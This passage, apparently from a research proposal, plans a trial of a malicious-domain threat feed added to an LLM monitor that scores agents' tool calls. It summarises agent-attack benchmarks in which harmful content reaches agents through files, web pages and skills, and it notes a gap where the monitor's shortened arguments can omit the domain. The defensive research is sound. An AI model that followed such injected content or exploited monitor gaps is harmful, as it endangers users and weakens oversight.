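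Researchers could start with the system that Pan and colleagues built. Its language model scores each call from the tool's name, a shortened copy of the arguments and a list of extracted features. Researchers could add a feed match to that list, but the lookup would have to use the full arguments because the shortened copy may omit the domain.

*EvoRiskBench* (Kuang, Luo and colleagues, 2026) already has 450 fixed attack tasks in which harmful content reaches an agent through files, web pages, skills and other routes. It measures both attack success and task completion. Up to 68.44% of attacks succeeded, depending on the model and the software around it. The team plans to release the tasks after safety checks. A feed could help only in tasks where the agent contacts an outside destination. *MalURLBench* (2026) tests agents on malicious links. Its risk score was highest for an agent that gives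 weather information, at 82.9%, and lower for food delivery and parcel tracking, so the trial should include several kinds of work.

If a benchmark uses invented attack domains, no real feed will list them. Researchers could simulate a feed that omits some of these domains, lists the others after delays based on measured ones, and includes false entries at a realistic rate. The simulated lookups in *LEGION* would be too favourable because they draw on the benchmark's own record of the attacks.

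The trial would need about 360 attack runs for each version to have an 80% chance of detecting a fall in the attack success rate from 40% to 30%. It would also need harmless tasks. If the feed broke none of 300 such tasks, the researchers could claim that it breaks fewer than 1%. An operator would still have to combine the results with a base rate and a false-match rate from real traffic.
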